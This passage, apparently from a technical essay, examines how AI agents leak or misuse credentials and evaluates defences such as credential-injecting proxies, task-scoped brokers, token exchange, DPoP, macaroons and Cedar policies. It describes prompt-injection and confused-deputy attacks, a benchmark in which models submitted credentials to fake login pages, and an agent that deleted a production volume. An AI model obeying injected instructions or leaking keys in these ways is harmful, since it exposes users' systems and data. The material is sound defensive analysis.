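Keys also end up in settings files. Claude Code asks the user before it runs a command, and if the user chooses not to be asked again, it saves the approved command in a settings file. Any password in the command is saved too, and becomes public if the developer uploads the project. Smith (2026), in *The Convenience Click That Put 2,539 Secrets on Public GitHub*, reports that the security company Apiiro found 2,539 distinct secrets in 1,994 repositories. *Caging the Agents* (2026), which describes a healthcare company's defenses, reports that an audit of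 the company's agents found keys in shell startup files, in workspace `.env` files, and in configuration files that every user of the machine could read.

Even a good model may give a secret to the wrong party. *CredLeakBench* (Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues, 2026) gave seven models the login details for fictional services and directed them to a mixture of genuine and fake login pages. When a user asked the agent to log in at a given link, the models submitted account information to fake pages in 19.9% to 76.7% of runs. Claude Opus 4.8 did so in 31.2%. When the agent was only sorting an inbox and nobody had asked it to log in, Opus's rate fell to 1.8%, but it also left 88.3% of the genuine requests undone, up from 6.6%. The 88.3% figure overstates the failure, because not logging in is reasonable when nobody has asked for it. Newer models may also do better. But most of the models improved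 on both measures when the researchers gave them a list of trusted addresses and told them to check it, and ordinary software can do that check without making a judgment.

The wider problem of leaked secrets is large. GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026) reports 28.65 million new secrets in public GitHub commits in 2025, 34% more than in 2024. Public commits grew by 43% over the same period, so the number of secrets per commit fell. GitGuardian sells software that finds leaked secrets, and its count depends on what its detectors recognize. It also seems to have revised its 2024 count. It originally published 23.8 million, which *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) still quotes, but its *The State of Secrets Sprawl Report 2026* (2026) gives 21 million. Measured against the original count, the rise in 2025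 is about 21%.

Most of those secrets have nothing to do with agents, but two of GitGuardian's figures are more directly relevant. Secrets appeared in 3.2% of commits that developers made with Claude Code, compared with 1.5% of all public commits, though GitGuardian cautions that people still decide what to accept and upload. It also found 24,008 secrets in configuration files for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of connecting models to tools, though only 2,117 were confirmed as valid. Popular setup guides often include instructions to put the key directly in the file.

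Leaked keys tend to keep working for a long time. Truffle Security, which makes a secret scanner, scanned 224 million public repositories and tried each credential it found (*GitHub Repos Exposed 543,699 Credentials. Nobody Revoked Them*, 2026). In July 2026, 543,699 of them still worked, and half of those had been public for more than two years.

Attackers can now find such keys quickly. Help Net Security's *AI agents now hunt leaked GitHub secrets faster than teams can revoke* (2026), a GitGuardian-sponsored article, summarizes a case that Microsoft disclosed in November 2026. An attacker's AI agent searched public GitHub, found an application's leaked secret and logged in with it. Five minutes after starting the search, it was copying data out of Azure Key Vault, Microsoft's service for storing secrets. Keeping those secrets in a vault was good practice, but it didn't protect them because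 the leaked secret gave access to the vault.

### One request through Agent Vault

Infisical, a company that sells secrets management, released an open-source proxy called Agent Vault in April 2026. A proxy is a program that passes requests between other programs. Infisical's *Credential Brokering for AI Agents, Explained* follows a request to GitHub through it. Suppose an agent wants to list the issues in a repository. Its environment contains a placeholder where the GitHub token would normally be, and it sends something like this:

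```
GET /repos/acme/site/issues
Host: api.github.com
Authorization: Bearer __github_token__
```

If the agent prints its token, or a stranger tricks it into sending the token somewhere, all that gets out is the string `__github_token__`.

Agent Vault has to replace the placeholder before the request reaches GitHub, which means reading and changing an encrypted message. HTTPS, the protocol that encrypts web traffic, is designed to prevent this. A server proves its identity with a certificate signed by an authority that the client trusts, and a proxy in the middle normally sees only scrambled data. An administrator gets around this by installing Agent Vault's own certificate authority as a trusted one on the agent's machine. The `HTTPS_PROXY` environment variable then routes traffic from the agent's programs through Agent Vault.

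According to Infisical's launch post, *Agent Vault*, the agent's program asks the proxy to open a tunnel to api.github.com and identifies itself with a session token. Agent Vault presents a certificate for api.github.com signed by its own certificate authority. The program accepts the certificate and sends the request, which Agent Vault can now decrypt. This is the same technique as a man-in-the-middle attack, except that the machine's owner has set it up.

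Agent Vault looks for a rule that covers api.github.com and this agent. If it finds one, it decrypts the real token in its own memory and swaps it for the placeholder. It then opens a new encrypted connection to GitHub, checks GitHub's certificate as usual and forwards the request. GitHub receives an ordinary call with a valid token, and its reply returns to the agent by the same route. The agent can't redirect the request after the tunnel opens, because Agent Vault fixes the destination at that point.

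Agents contact services through command-line tools, programming libraries, MCP tools and direct API calls. Nearly all of these end up as HTTPS requests, so Infisical chose to work at that level. Its earlier gateway covered only MCP. With the new approach, the agent's tools don't need to change, and a company can replace a key in one place without touching any agent. Infisical lists Anthropic, Vercel, Cloudflare and LangChain among the companies that have built something similar.

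The product and its name have changed quickly. In July, Infisical announced a commercial successor in *Agent Proxy*, explaining that the original had wrongly combined storing secrets with adding them to requests. Infisical has since deprecated Agent Proxy in favor of a new product, again called Agent Vault.

### Connecting it to HashiCorp Vault

TRM Labs wanted to use the original Agent Vault for its internal agents but kept its secrets in HashiCorp Vault, a widely used secret store that Agent Vault couldn't read. Bhinder copied Agent Vault's source code, added HashiCorp Vault as a full storage option and offered the change back to Infisical. He chose this over writing a small program to translate between the two because he expected such a program to break the first time either changed.

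He built the tool with an AI agent running Claude Opus 4.8, even though its purpose is to keep secrets from agents. He knew this was slightly odd, and most of his account describes the precautions he took. Before the agent wrote any code, he wrote a test plan describing what a user should be able to do. After every significant change, the agent also had to produce a demonstration that ran against a real copy of HashiCorp Vault. The demonstration showed a secret in HashiCorp Vault and its arrival in Agent Vault, then sent a request through the proxy and confirmed that the service received the real key. Finally, it changed the secret at the source and checked that the new value came through.

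Agents that had not written the code reviewed it with instructions to assume it was wrong. They found a numbering clash that would have stopped the service from starting. They also found that the program loaded a token at startup but never checked it, so a bad token would have failed silently later. Bhinder made the final decisions.

His post shows that a company can add injection without moving its secrets to a new store or changing how it replaces them. It doesn't show how well this works in daily use, since he gives no operating figures and Infisical had not yet accepted the change when he wrote. He also says that the secrets stay where they are, which isn't quite right if Agent Vault keeps a synchronized copy, as the demonstration suggests. That copy would also need protecting. Infisical may have had this problem in mind a month later, when it argued that a broker should fetch secrets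 on demand and leave storage to something else.

### Where the protection can fail

Injection helps only if the agent cannot read the proxy's files or memory. Infisical recommends running the proxy on a separate machine, because containers on the same machine share a kernel, the core of the operating system, and "a single kernel exploit voids the entire threat model." *Caging the Agents* describes a less strict design, in which the proxy runs in a container next to the agent's and the agent reaches it at a local address. This is still far better than leaving keys in `.env` files, and Infisical's current product page, *Agent Vault*, now offers the same arrangement as an option. Most companies are more likely to have problems with a careless agent than with one that breaks out through the kernel.

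The agent still holds one credential, the token that identifies it to the proxy. According to Infisical's documentation for Agent Proxy, a thief who gets this token can't use it to read any secret, but can send traffic through the same services as the agent. The proxy should therefore accept connections only from the private network where the agents run. Agent Proxy rechecks each agent's permissions every 60 seconds by default, so a withdrawn permission may keep working for up to a minute, which is far longer than the PocketOS deletion took.

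The proxy also has to tie each key to its destination. If it added the GitHub token to any request that contained the placeholder, an attacker could get the agent to send such a request to the attacker's server, and the proxy would deliver the real token. With a rule that covers only api.github.com, the attacker's server receives only the placeholder. The proxy does the address check that the models in the phishing tests did unreliably, and the model can't override it.

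A rule that limits where the proxy can send a secret can still be too loose. Infisical writes that its proxy replaces the placeholder "wherever it appears in the outbound request." If that includes the body of the request, an agent could post a public GitHub comment containing `__github_token__`, and the proxy would publish the real token in its place. A safe rule would have the proxy replace the placeholder only in the part of the request where the service expects a key. A service can also expose the key to the agent by repeating it in a reply, for example in a detailed error message.

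Finally, the administrator has to block every route out of the agent's environment except the proxy. Setting the `HTTPS_PROXY` variable isn't enough, because programs can ignore it and, as Infisical points out, an agent can unset it. An agent that bypasses the proxy still has only placeholders for the vaulted keys, but it escapes the logs and restrictions and can use any other key it finds.

That matters for a case like PocketOS, where the agent found a stray token in a file. Putting new keys in a vault doesn't remove old ones left in files. A proxy on the only route out could have helped, depending on its settings. By default, Agent Proxy forwards requests to unlisted services unchanged so that agents can read documentation and install packages. A request to Railway with the stray token would therefore have gone through. With the stricter setting, the proxy would have rejected it. If Railway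 had been on the list, the original Agent Vault would have replaced the stray token with the approved one.

Some credentials don't fit this method. Agent Proxy handles only web traffic, so it can't protect an SSH key such as a GitHub deploy key. For those keys, Infisical recommends switching to HTTPS and a token. The company advertises support for SSH and database connections in its new Agent Vault, which is still in preview. The proxy can also read everything the agent sends to the services it handles. Because it collects many keys in one place, a breach of the proxy or the store behind it would be serious.

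### The Corvic experiments

Kenney and colleagues at Corvic AI tested their own product, Corvic Security Vault, to see whether a system of this kind hides its keys. An agent's code names a connector, a stored record of one service's address and key, and the vault adds the key to requests for that address.

The case begins with a five-stage threat chain. In the first stage, introduction, someone puts a reusable secret where the model can see it, for example by pasting a token into a chat. In the second, propagation, the secret is copied into the conversation history, logs, memory and generated code. In the third, the trigger, something such as a prompt injection or an ordinary error leads the agent to disclose or misuse the secret. In the fourth, execution, the token's permissions allow data to be read, deleted or published. In the fifth, persistence, a long-lived token keeps working outside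 the original conversation for anyone who has copied it.

Kenney and colleagues argue that a vault can eliminate the first two stages by design, because a secret that never enters the conversation leaves no copies there. They add that a vault does not address the last two. That seems right about execution but too pessimistic about persistence, since an attacker who never gets a token cannot reuse it elsewhere. Kenney and colleagues' own scores for replaying stolen tokens fall by more than half.

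On September 27, 2026, the researchers ran two experiments inside the product's sandbox, each with access to one connector. In the first, they used FRED, the economic database of the Federal Reserve Bank of St. Louis, and searched the sandbox for any trace of a key. In the second, they used GitHub and mainly tested whether the vault added the key to the right requests and no others. Before running either experiment, they wrote down the result they expected from each individual test.

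For the positive control, a request that should succeed, code containing no credential requested the logged-in user's identity from GitHub. GitHub returned an authenticated identity, so the vault must have added the key. The negative controls were requests that should not carry a key. Three echo services, which send back whatever they receive, returned no credential, and OpenAI's API, which had no connector, returned a missing-authentication error. The positive control was needed to interpret these results, because a sandbox with no working key would also have passed the leak tests.

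The other probes looked for keys where an intruder would. None of the sandbox's 20 environment variables contained anything resembling a credential, and none of 12 common locations for credential files existed. Requests timed out when sent to the internal addresses where Amazon's and Google's clouds give programs credentials. In all, 16 probes in seven categories gave the expected result. Five tested whether the vault tied the key to its address, one tested authorized use, and there were two each for environment variables, files, leaks to other sites, whether code could observe the key, and access to cloud credentials.

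The FRED connector did not work because someone had set it up to send the key in a header, while FRED requires the key in the web address of the request. FRED returned an error saying the key was missing. Kenney and colleagues scored this separately as a failure of function, so it does not count against the 16. They take it as a reminder that a centrally stored key can still be misconfigured. The failure also slightly weakens the first experiment, because nothing in that run proved that the vault was attaching the FRED key to any request. The fact that the echo services did not receive the FRED key is therefore weaker evidence than the same result with GitHub.

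The researchers tested their own product with sixteen hand-picked probes. These can show that the mechanism works in the cases tested but not how often it fails, a limit the researchers acknowledge by calling the study small and purposive. They did not test redirects, token theft during renewal, or what happens if an attacker controls a permitted service. They also did not verify how the product encrypts its secrets or separates one customer from another.

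The paper then scores eight threats before and after adding the vault. Each score is likelihood times impact, both rated from 1 to 5, so the maximum is 25.

| Threat | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Secret pasted into a prompt | 25 | 4 |
| Prompt injection through material the agent reads | 25 | 12 |
| Credential sent to the wrong destination | 20 | 4 |
| Credential found in the agent's environment | 20 | 4 |
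| Over-privileged connector | 20 | 15 |
| Reuse of a long-lived token | 20 | 8 |
| Leak through logs or error messages | 16 | 8 |
| Misconfigured connector | 9 | 6 |

These are expert judgments by people who built the product, so the fall from 25 to 4 is not a measured 84% reduction in risk. The experiments support some rows much better than others because they tested directly for credentials in the environment and at the wrong destinations, but included no prompt injection or over-privileged connector. Kenney and colleagues acknowledge that the most valuable next step would be to run an established prompt injection test against the vault.

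The ranking is still informative, because a company assessing its own product has an incentive to be generous. The over-privileged connector ends with the highest score, 15, because a vault does not narrow a key's permissions, so a token with write access keeps it. Prompt injection comes next with 12.

### An agent with no secret can still use it

An agent that never sees a key can still do almost everything the key permits by sending requests through the proxy. If an injected instruction causes it to try to delete a repository, the agent sends the delete request with a placeholder for the key, and the proxy, acting as what Hardy called a confused deputy, adds a valid token.

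Credential injection might have changed little at PocketOS. Suppose Crane had put his account-wide Railway token in a vault and given the agent a Railway connector for managing domains. When the agent decided to delete a volume, the proxy would have attached the token to its request. The database would have been gone just as quickly, and the agent wouldn't have had to search for a key. The vault would have saved the database only if nobody had connected the agent to Railway, or if the token behind the connector had carried narrower permissions.

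Credential injection makes an attacker's job harder. Without a copy of the key, the attacker has to act through the agent, from inside the company's network, while the proxy records each request. The company can stop the attack by cutting off that one agent. Injection helps against theft but does little about an agent's own mistakes, which are mainly what narrow scope limits.

Zandi, Sabic and Voytenko (2026), engineers at the cloud hosting company Vercel, argue in *The end of credential sprawl for agents* that putting a long-lived token in a vault makes it harder to steal but "no less dangerous once stolen." Vercel's product instead gives code a short-lived token for each task, limited in scope where the service allows it, and identifies the code by a signed statement, much as AWS does for GitHub jobs. Infisical's complaint about short-lived tokens is that an agent can still leak them. Both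 companies are right, though each is describing the weakness that its own product addresses. The two methods are also easy to combine. If a proxy holds a GitHub installation token for one repository, the agent can't leak the token or use it on anything else.

For services that offer no narrow keys, the proxy can add its own limits, since it already reads every request. At launch, Infisical's Agent Vault mostly matched a destination and added a key, with request-level restrictions planned for later. Infisical now describes "access bundles" that restrict an agent to particular MCP tools, HTTP methods (such as GET for reading and POST for sending data), and addresses within a service. Sessions expire on a schedule, and an administrator can revoke one while the agent is running.

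Rules like these work well when a service uses different addresses and methods for different operations, as GitHub's main API does. Railway's API instead receives every instruction as a POST request to a single address, with the operation named in the body, so a rule about methods and addresses can't distinguish adding a domain from deleting a volume. To allow one and block the other, the proxy would have to read the body, recognize the operation and check whether this agent had permission for it.

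## The case for a broker that issues and checks each grant

A broker, the service between agents and the systems they use, makes checks of this kind. When a task begins, the broker creates a grant, a recorded permission for one agent to perform stated operations on stated resources under stated conditions. It then compares every request with the grant. The grant ends when the task does, so the agent carries no permissions into its next task.

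Silverlock's *The Agent Access Model*, which the internet infrastructure company Cloudflare published in August 2026, favors reducing the agent's authority, so that there is less to judge, over making each access decision smarter. *Delegation Without Trust* (Dantuluri and Sundi, 2026) proposes a strict test for any system that limits an agent's authority: even if an attacker controls every word the model writes, the agent should be unable to exceed the authority that someone explicitly gave it. A rule in the prompt fails this test, and so does any design in which the model decides whether its own action is permitted.

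A narrow enough key would pass, but many services don't offer one. A broker can add limits that the service lacks, such as allowing refunds only to one named customer and only up to $100.

### The ceiling is an intersection

In Silverlock's design, the broker works out the limits of a task before the agent starts. It combines what the user may do, what the agent may do, what the task template permits and what the owner of the resource permits. A template is a description of one type of job, which somebody writes once and the broker fills in for each run. If U, A, T and R are the sets of operations that each of these allows, the agent's ceiling is their intersection:

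C = U ∩ A ∩ T ∩ R

Suppose Dana in customer support asks an agent to fix a double charge for customer 4417. The company has a template for billing corrections, and its billing team has set rules for all agents.

| Operation | Dana | Agent | Template | Billing team | Ceiling |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read customer 4417's orders | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Read other customers' orders | Yes | Yes | No | Yes | No |
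| Refund customer 4417 | Up to $500 | Up to $200 | Up to $300 | Up to $100 | Up to $100 |
| Change a subscription price | No | Yes | Yes | Yes | No |
| Delete a customer record | Yes | No | No | No | No |

The lowest limit applies to the refund. The price change is a small example of the confused deputy problem. Dana isn't allowed to change prices, and she can't get around that by asking an agent that is. The template's author probably shouldn't have included price changes, but this did no harm because another column ruled them out.

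The ceiling stays fixed while the agent works. The agent can request less, but if it needs more, someone has to authorize a new task. An instruction hidden in a customer's email therefore can't raise the refund limit, even if the agent tries to follow it.

An intersection restricts an agent least when the user is an administrator. Crane could delete any volume in his Railway account, so his own authority would have ruled out nothing, and most of the limits would have had to come from the template. The rule can also be too strict. It would have stopped Tymshare's compiler from overwriting the billing file, because the user had no permission to write there. But users presumably couldn't write to the compiler's statistics file either, so the compiler couldn't have kept its statistics. An agent that needs authority of its own, for example to update a log, needs a separate grant.

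The rule also assumes one user per task. Silverlock gives the example of an agent that serves a team including Alice, who can see revenue data, and Bob, who can't. If the agent summarizes a revenue document for Alice and then uses the summary to answer Bob, it leaks the data. If the broker limits the agent to what both may see, the agent becomes less useful to Alice. Silverlock knows of no widely deployed system that solves this end to end. For now, he suggests either keeping each person's work separate or limiting the agent to what everyone on the team may see.

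### Recording who acts for whom

To apply the intersection, a service has to know that a request comes from an agent and that the agent is working for Dana. The 2020 internet standard *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, by Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, defines a way to put both facts in one token.

The agent's software sends two tokens to the company's authorization server, which issues tokens for its services. One identifies Dana (the subject token) and the other identifies the agent (the actor token). The request also names the service the agent wants to use and the scope it wants. If the server approves, it returns a new token, whose contents might look like this:

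```
{
  "iss": "https://login.example.com",
  "aud": "https://billing.example.com",
  "exp": 1796480400,
  "scope": "orders.read refunds.create",
  "sub": "dana@example.com",
  "act": { "sub": "support-agent" }
}
```

The `sub` claim identifies Dana, and the `act` claim identifies the agent acting for her. Jones and colleagues call this delegation. If the software sends only Dana's token, the result is impersonation, where the new token identifies only Dana and the billing service can't distinguish the agent from her. Many companies already let agents work this way, usually by giving them a user's token. They then can't set a separate limit for the agent, and their logs attribute the agent's actions to the user.

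Dana's original token can also contain a `may_act` claim, which names a party that may act for her. The authorization server can use this claim to refuse an exchange requested by any other program.

If the support agent hands part of the job to another agent, a second exchange puts one `act` claim inside another. The outer claim names the current agent and the inner one names the support agent, so an investigator can follow the chain back to Dana. But the standard treats earlier actors as "informational only" and forbids services from considering them in access decisions. A billing service therefore can't refuse a request on the grounds that it distrusts an earlier agent in the chain. Token exchange also has no standard way to validate the path of delegation, according to a draft published through the IETF (2026), the body that develops internet standards. The draft proposes six ways to add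 one.

Token exchange also doesn't narrow permissions by itself. The client can ask for a smaller scope, but the server's policy determines what it issues. Lynch and Panchal's *Secure AI agent authentication using HashiCorp Vault dynamic secrets* shows an exchange through Microsoft's identity service in which the agent asks for `Products.Read`, but the token printed as the result permits reading, listing, writing and deleting products. The two samples may come from different runs, but a developer who copied the request and never decoded the token wouldn't notice the extra permissions.

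The new token may also remain valid after the original stops working. The standard treats an exchange as a one-time event, so revoking Dana's original token doesn't necessarily revoke the agent's. Unless the broker tracks the link between the two tokens, it has to rely on the agent's token expiring early.

### Tokens that a thief cannot use

A token from an exchange is usually still a bearer token. In *OAuth 2.0 Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP)*, Fett, Campbell and colleagues describe how to bind a token to a cryptographic key so that a copy of the token is useless without the key.

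The client creates a private and public key pair. When it asks for a token, it signs the request with the private key, and the authorization server ties the new token to the public key. The client then has to sign a new proof for every request. The proof covers the HTTP method, the address, the time, a unique identifier and a hash of the token, which is a short code computed from it. The service checks the signature and confirms that the proof matches both the token and the request. A thief who has the token but not the private key can't produce a valid proof.

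The proof leaves out the body of the request and anything after a question mark in the address. Fett and colleagues chose this because different programs format the same message slightly differently, which makes signing all of it difficult. They rely on HTTPS to prevent anyone from altering the message in transit. The proof therefore shows who sent a request but little about what it contains. On Railway's API, where every instruction is a POST to the same address, a proof for adding a domain would cover the same method and address as one for deleting a volume.

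The private key's location also matters. Malicious code running inside the client can request a signature, and Fett and colleagues consider DPoP unable to prevent this. An agent that could read its own key could leak it along with the token. Silverlock keeps the key in the harness, the software that surrounds the model and carries out its tool calls. A hijacked agent can still misuse the token through the harness, but it can't leak the key that anyone else would need to use the token.

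### Narrowing along a chain of agents

Agents increasingly divide work among sub-agents. If the support agent asks a sub-agent to find the duplicate charge, the sub-agent needs to read the orders but not to issue refunds. Each handover should narrow the credential, as an AWS session policy does for a single job.

Macaroons, a type of token that a group of researchers, mostly at Google, introduced in 2014, let the holder do this without contacting the issuer. They use a function called HMAC, which turns a key and a message into a short code. Nobody can compute the code without the key or work backward from the code to the key. The issuer has a secret key K and computes a signature for the token's identifier. Each added condition, or caveat, produces a new signature, with the previous signature as the key:

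s₀ = HMAC(K, identifier)
s₁ = HMAC(s₀, "customer 4417 only")
s₂ = HMAC(s₁, "read only")

The support agent's token contains the identifier, the first caveat and s₁. To make a weaker token for the sub-agent, the support agent adds "read only", replaces s₁ with s₂ and passes the token on. The sub-agent can add more caveats, but it can't remove "read only", because that would require s₁, which it can't recover from s₂. The service that receives the token uses K to recompute the whole chain, then checks that the request satisfies every caveat. The permissions are again an intersection, so adding "refunds allowed" doesn't override "read only".

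A token that anyone can narrow offline is fast and convenient, but the issuer has no record of each handover to a sub-agent. Dantuluri and Sundi use the same kind of signature but require agents to go through the broker. The broker issues a weaker token for the sub-agent, ties it to that sub-agent's identity and records the link. Revoking the parent's token also disables every token derived from it. This requires one extra call for each handover, which seems worthwhile for a company that may need to stop a whole chain of agents quickly.

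### Rules outside the model

The system still has to compare each request with the grant. A policy engine is software that does this by evaluating written rules and returning allow or deny, without using a language model. Cedar, an open-source policy language that Amazon released in 2023, is a good example because its logic is simple enough to state completely.

A Cedar request has four parts: the principal (who is asking), the action, the resource, and the context, which holds other facts such as the amount of a refund. A policy either permits or forbids requests that match it. Dana's task might lead to these two:

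```
permit (
    principal == Agent::"support-agent",
    action == Action::"IssueRefund",
    resource == Customer::"4417"
)
when { context.amount <= 100 };

forbid (
    principal,
    action == Action::"IssueRefund",
    resource
)
when { resource.underFraudReview };
```

Cedar allows a request if at least one `permit` policy matches and no `forbid` policy does. It denies everything else. An $80 refund to customer 4417 goes through unless the customer is under fraud review, when the `forbid` policy overrides the `permit` policy. Cedar denies an $80 refund to customer 4418 because no policy permits it. The order of the policies doesn't matter, so an administrator can add a `forbid` policy without worrying that a `permit` policy elsewhere will cancel it.

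If a policy refers to missing data, such as an `underFraudReview` field that a customer record lacks, Cedar ignores that policy and continues with the others. Ignoring a permission is safe because it can only lead to more denials, but ignoring a prohibition may let the refund go through. Cedar's validator can catch many such mistakes in advance by checking policies against a description of the data, and a company that relies on prohibitions should use it.

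Permissions in Cedar are also additive. If one policy permits refunds to customer 4417 and another permits refunds to everyone, the agent can refund everyone. To get an intersection, the broker has to evaluate the user's policies, the agent's and the others separately, and approve the request only if every set allows it. Alternatively, an administrator can write the ceiling as a policy that forbids every request unless it falls within set limits.

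The engine can decide correctly only if its facts are reliable, so the refund amount has to come from the request itself and the fraud flag from the company's own records. If the agent supplied either, an injected instruction could change the decision. Silverlock adds that the broker should freeze the request, including every detail that affects what it does, before checking it, and then send exactly that version. Otherwise the agent might get approval for an $80 refund and send one for $800.

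### Cloudflare, CB4A and HashiCorp Vault

Three designs from 2026 combine these parts, and they differ mainly in what the agent receives and how long the broker stays involved.

Silverlock's model is a reference architecture: it describes what each part must guarantee and leaves the details to others. His example is a finance team's agent that compares a payment company's report with two internal ledgers every night. Before the agent runs, the Task-Scoped Access Engine calculates its maximum permissions. For ten minutes, the agent may fetch the report, read the two ledgers, contact the payment company's support desk in defined cases, and post a summary to one channel. The Agent Identity Broker then exchanges the agent's broad identity for a token that covers only this run.

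The access engine keeps checking every action after that. The harness enforces the engine's decisions on tool calls, where it can see the arguments. The network blocks connections to any destination that isn't on the list, so a bug in the harness doesn't open the network. But the harness and the network depend on the same policy data, so Silverlock requires both to refuse everything if that data becomes unavailable. Silverlock's Trust Ratchet, covered in a later section, removes permissions during a task before it lets sensitive data reach the agent.

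*Credential Broker for Agents (CB4A)* (Hartman, 2026) splits the broker into two components. One decides on requests and never touches a secret. The other fetches secrets and issues tokens, but only when it receives a signed decision from the first. To get a token, the agent submits a signed form with its identity, the service, the action, the resource and how long it needs access. The form also has a space for a reason, which is logged for investigators. The deciding component must ignore the reason, because a hijacked agent could write a persuasive one.

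After approval, CB4A can supply access in three ways:

- It can keep the secret and add it to the agent's requests, as Agent Vault does.
- It can use the secret to create a temporary token and give that to the agent. Hartman recommends this wherever the service supports it.
- It can give the agent the real long-lived key and schedule its revocation. Hartman discourages this and reserves it for old services that offer nothing else. It also contradicts the draft's opening promise that agents never hold such keys.

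The clear benefit of the split is that the component that interprets forms from possibly hijacked agents holds no secrets. Hartman claims that an attacker who compromises one component does not get the other, which is only partly true. An attacker who controls the deciding component can't read the vault, but can presumably approve requests and collect the tokens. An attacker who controls the other component can capture real secrets as it uses them, which Hartman rates as the design's one critical threat.

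This danger applies to every broker. Hartman motivates his proposal with the case of LiteLLM, a gateway that holds companies' keys for AI services. In March 2026, attackers added credential-stealing code to its software packages, and by an estimate he cites, the wider campaign affected about 500,000 corporate identities. He presents this as a reason to build a broker, and short-lived tokens would have been less useful to the thieves. But LiteLLM, like a broker, sat between programs and the systems they used, and it was a valuable target because so many keys passed through it.

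CB4A is an individual internet draft with no official standing. Hartman of the SANS Institute, a security training organization, submitted it on March 29, 2026. Anyone can submit such a draft, and the IETF had not adopted this one. It expired on September 30, apparently without a newer version.

HashiCorp's design is a product that companies can buy. It began as an early-access program. HashiCorp's *Advancing AI agent security in Vault* announced a public preview a few weeks later, and HashiCorp has since made the features generally available in Vault Enterprise 2.1. An administrator registers each agent, and the agent gets a signed token from the company's identity provider. The token states what the agent may do in this session. HashiCorp gives this example, which permits reading one secret:

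```
"authorization_details": [
  {
    "capabilities": ["read"],
    "path": "secrets/my-secret",
    "type": "vault:path_access"
  }
]
```

The agent presents the token with every request to Vault. According to HashiCorp's *What is agentic IAM?*, when an agent acts for a user, Vault allows only what the user's policies, the agent's ceiling and the token's details all permit. By default Vault rejects a token without these details, but an administrator can make them optional, in which case Vault checks a token that lacks them against only the user's policies and the agent's ceiling. HashiCorp's *Agent registry* explains that the default ceiling also stops an agent from using an administrator's permissions to change its own limits.

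The ceiling applies only when an agent acts for a user. An agent that runs on its own, such as a nightly scheduled job, gets its own standing policies, which the token can narrow. Someone has to write those policies as carefully as a ceiling, because no user's permissions further limit what the agent can do.

Vault's "per-request" checks also cover only requests to Vault, which doesn't monitor what the agent or its tools do with a credential after it is released. Vault can reduce this problem by creating temporary credentials with narrower permissions, but this isn't automatic in the pattern Lynch and Panchal describe, which uses an older login method. In their sample logs, a user named Bob asks the agent to list all products, and Vault issues a database login called `readwrite` because Bob's group has that role. The login is temporary and the logs trace it to Bob, but its permissions are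 based on his group's role rather than his request. A task template would have limited the login to reading.

| | Agent Access Model | CB4A | HashiCorp Vault |
|---|---|---|---|
| Status | Reference architecture | Individual draft, expired | Product |
| Sets the limit | User, agent, template and resource owner | Written policy and the agent's usual behavior | User, agent ceiling and token details |
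| Agent receives | A token for one task, bound to a key in the harness | Usually a temporary token, bound to the agent's own key | A secret or temporary credential, directly or through a tool |
| Checks | Every tool call and network connection | Every request for a credential | Every request to Vault |

Silverlock's design offers the most control and requires the most work, because the harness has to interpret every operation it allows. CB4A and Vault are easier to add to existing systems, but they rely more on the permissions each service offers. Like Infisical's proxy, all three depend on the agent having no other way to reach the services. Hartman recommends blocking direct connections and searching the logs of the services behind the broker for requests missing from the broker's records.

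Other companies and engineers are developing similar approaches. *Kong launches Token Vault to secure AI agent access* (Mitchell, 2026) reports on a product that supplies credentials at the moment of use, and *Credential Delegation Protocol for AI Agents in Multi-System Environments* (Sweeney, 2026) is another individual draft, submitted in July. There is no agreed common standard yet.

### A broker under attack

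Dantuluri and Sundi built a small broker and tried to break it. They start from eight requirements:

1. A service can trace every agent's authority back to a person.
2. Each handover can only narrow it.
3. A token works only for the program that received it.
4. Tokens expire quickly.
5. Keys change automatically.
6. Revocation reaches every checkpoint promptly.
7. A tamper-evident log covers every privileged action.
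8. Software outside the model makes every access decision.

They consider the last the most important, because if the model controls access, whoever hijacks the model does too.

They first looked at what developers get by default from four popular systems for building or connecting agents. They ran LangGraph with a scripted agent, inspected the code of CrewAI and AutoGen, and read the MCP authorization specification. LangGraph, CrewAI and AutoGen met none of the eight requirements. The researchers don't call this a defect, since none of the three claims to be an access control system. MCP partly met some requirements, for example by tying each token to one server. These ratings are judgments, and the paper's two tables disagree about MCP on key changes, revocation and logs. MCP may also be less secure in practice than its specification suggests, since Dantuluri and Sundi cite a survey of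 7,973 live MCP servers in which more than 40% offered their tools with no authentication.

The broker is about 160 lines of Python. Each agent has its own identity, and the broker checks the signature, revocation status, sender and token caveats on every tool call. The researchers compared it with a simple system in which all agents share one broad bearer token and the model decides what is permitted.

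The tests included four attacks on both systems: a confused deputy, a stolen token, an agent that tries to gain extra permissions, and a compromised sub-agent. All four succeeded against the simple system and failed against the broker. The broker also resisted eleven further attacks on its own design, such as removing a caveat, reusing an expired token or passing on another agent's token. It rejected all 200,000 forged tokens, some random and some altered copies of real ones.

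The researchers ran 2,000 random scenarios in an invented company with 8,100 possible actions. A compromised sub-agent could reach all 8,100 with the shared token, but an average of 1.5 with the broker. Each check took about 2.6 microseconds on a laptop, and each token exchange took about 5.4 microseconds.

These results show that the code works as designed, which is useful but limited evidence. The figure of 1.5 is the average size of the tasks the researchers assigned, because the broker confined each sub-agent to its task. They acknowledge this and put more weight on the finding that a sub-agent's reach stays the same as the company grows. The forged tokens test for programming errors, since nobody would expect to guess an HMAC signature in 200,000 tries. The timing leaves out the network trip to a real broker and any lookup of company records. Even so, a delay of under 10 milliseconds,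 Hartman's target for an automatic decision, would hardly be noticeable next to the time a model takes to respond.

One attack worked, as the researchers expected. A thief who can also present the victim's identity can use a stolen token. The broker relies on another system to verify each program's identity, so a weakness in that system defeats the key binding.

The claimed protection against the confused deputy covers only actions outside the agent's grant. If Dana's agent is allowed to refund customer 4417 and a hidden instruction causes it to issue an undeserved $90 refund, the request is within the grant and the broker will approve it. The experiments used no live model, and the researchers haven't connected the broker to any of the systems they examined or released its code. Both researchers work for VotalAI, which sells a product based on the same principles.

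### Who writes the templates

The obvious objection is that somebody has to write a template before anyone knows what steps the agent will take. If the template is too narrow, the agent fails. After a few failures, someone will widen it until people stop complaining, and the company will have broad permissions again, with a more complex system for managing them.

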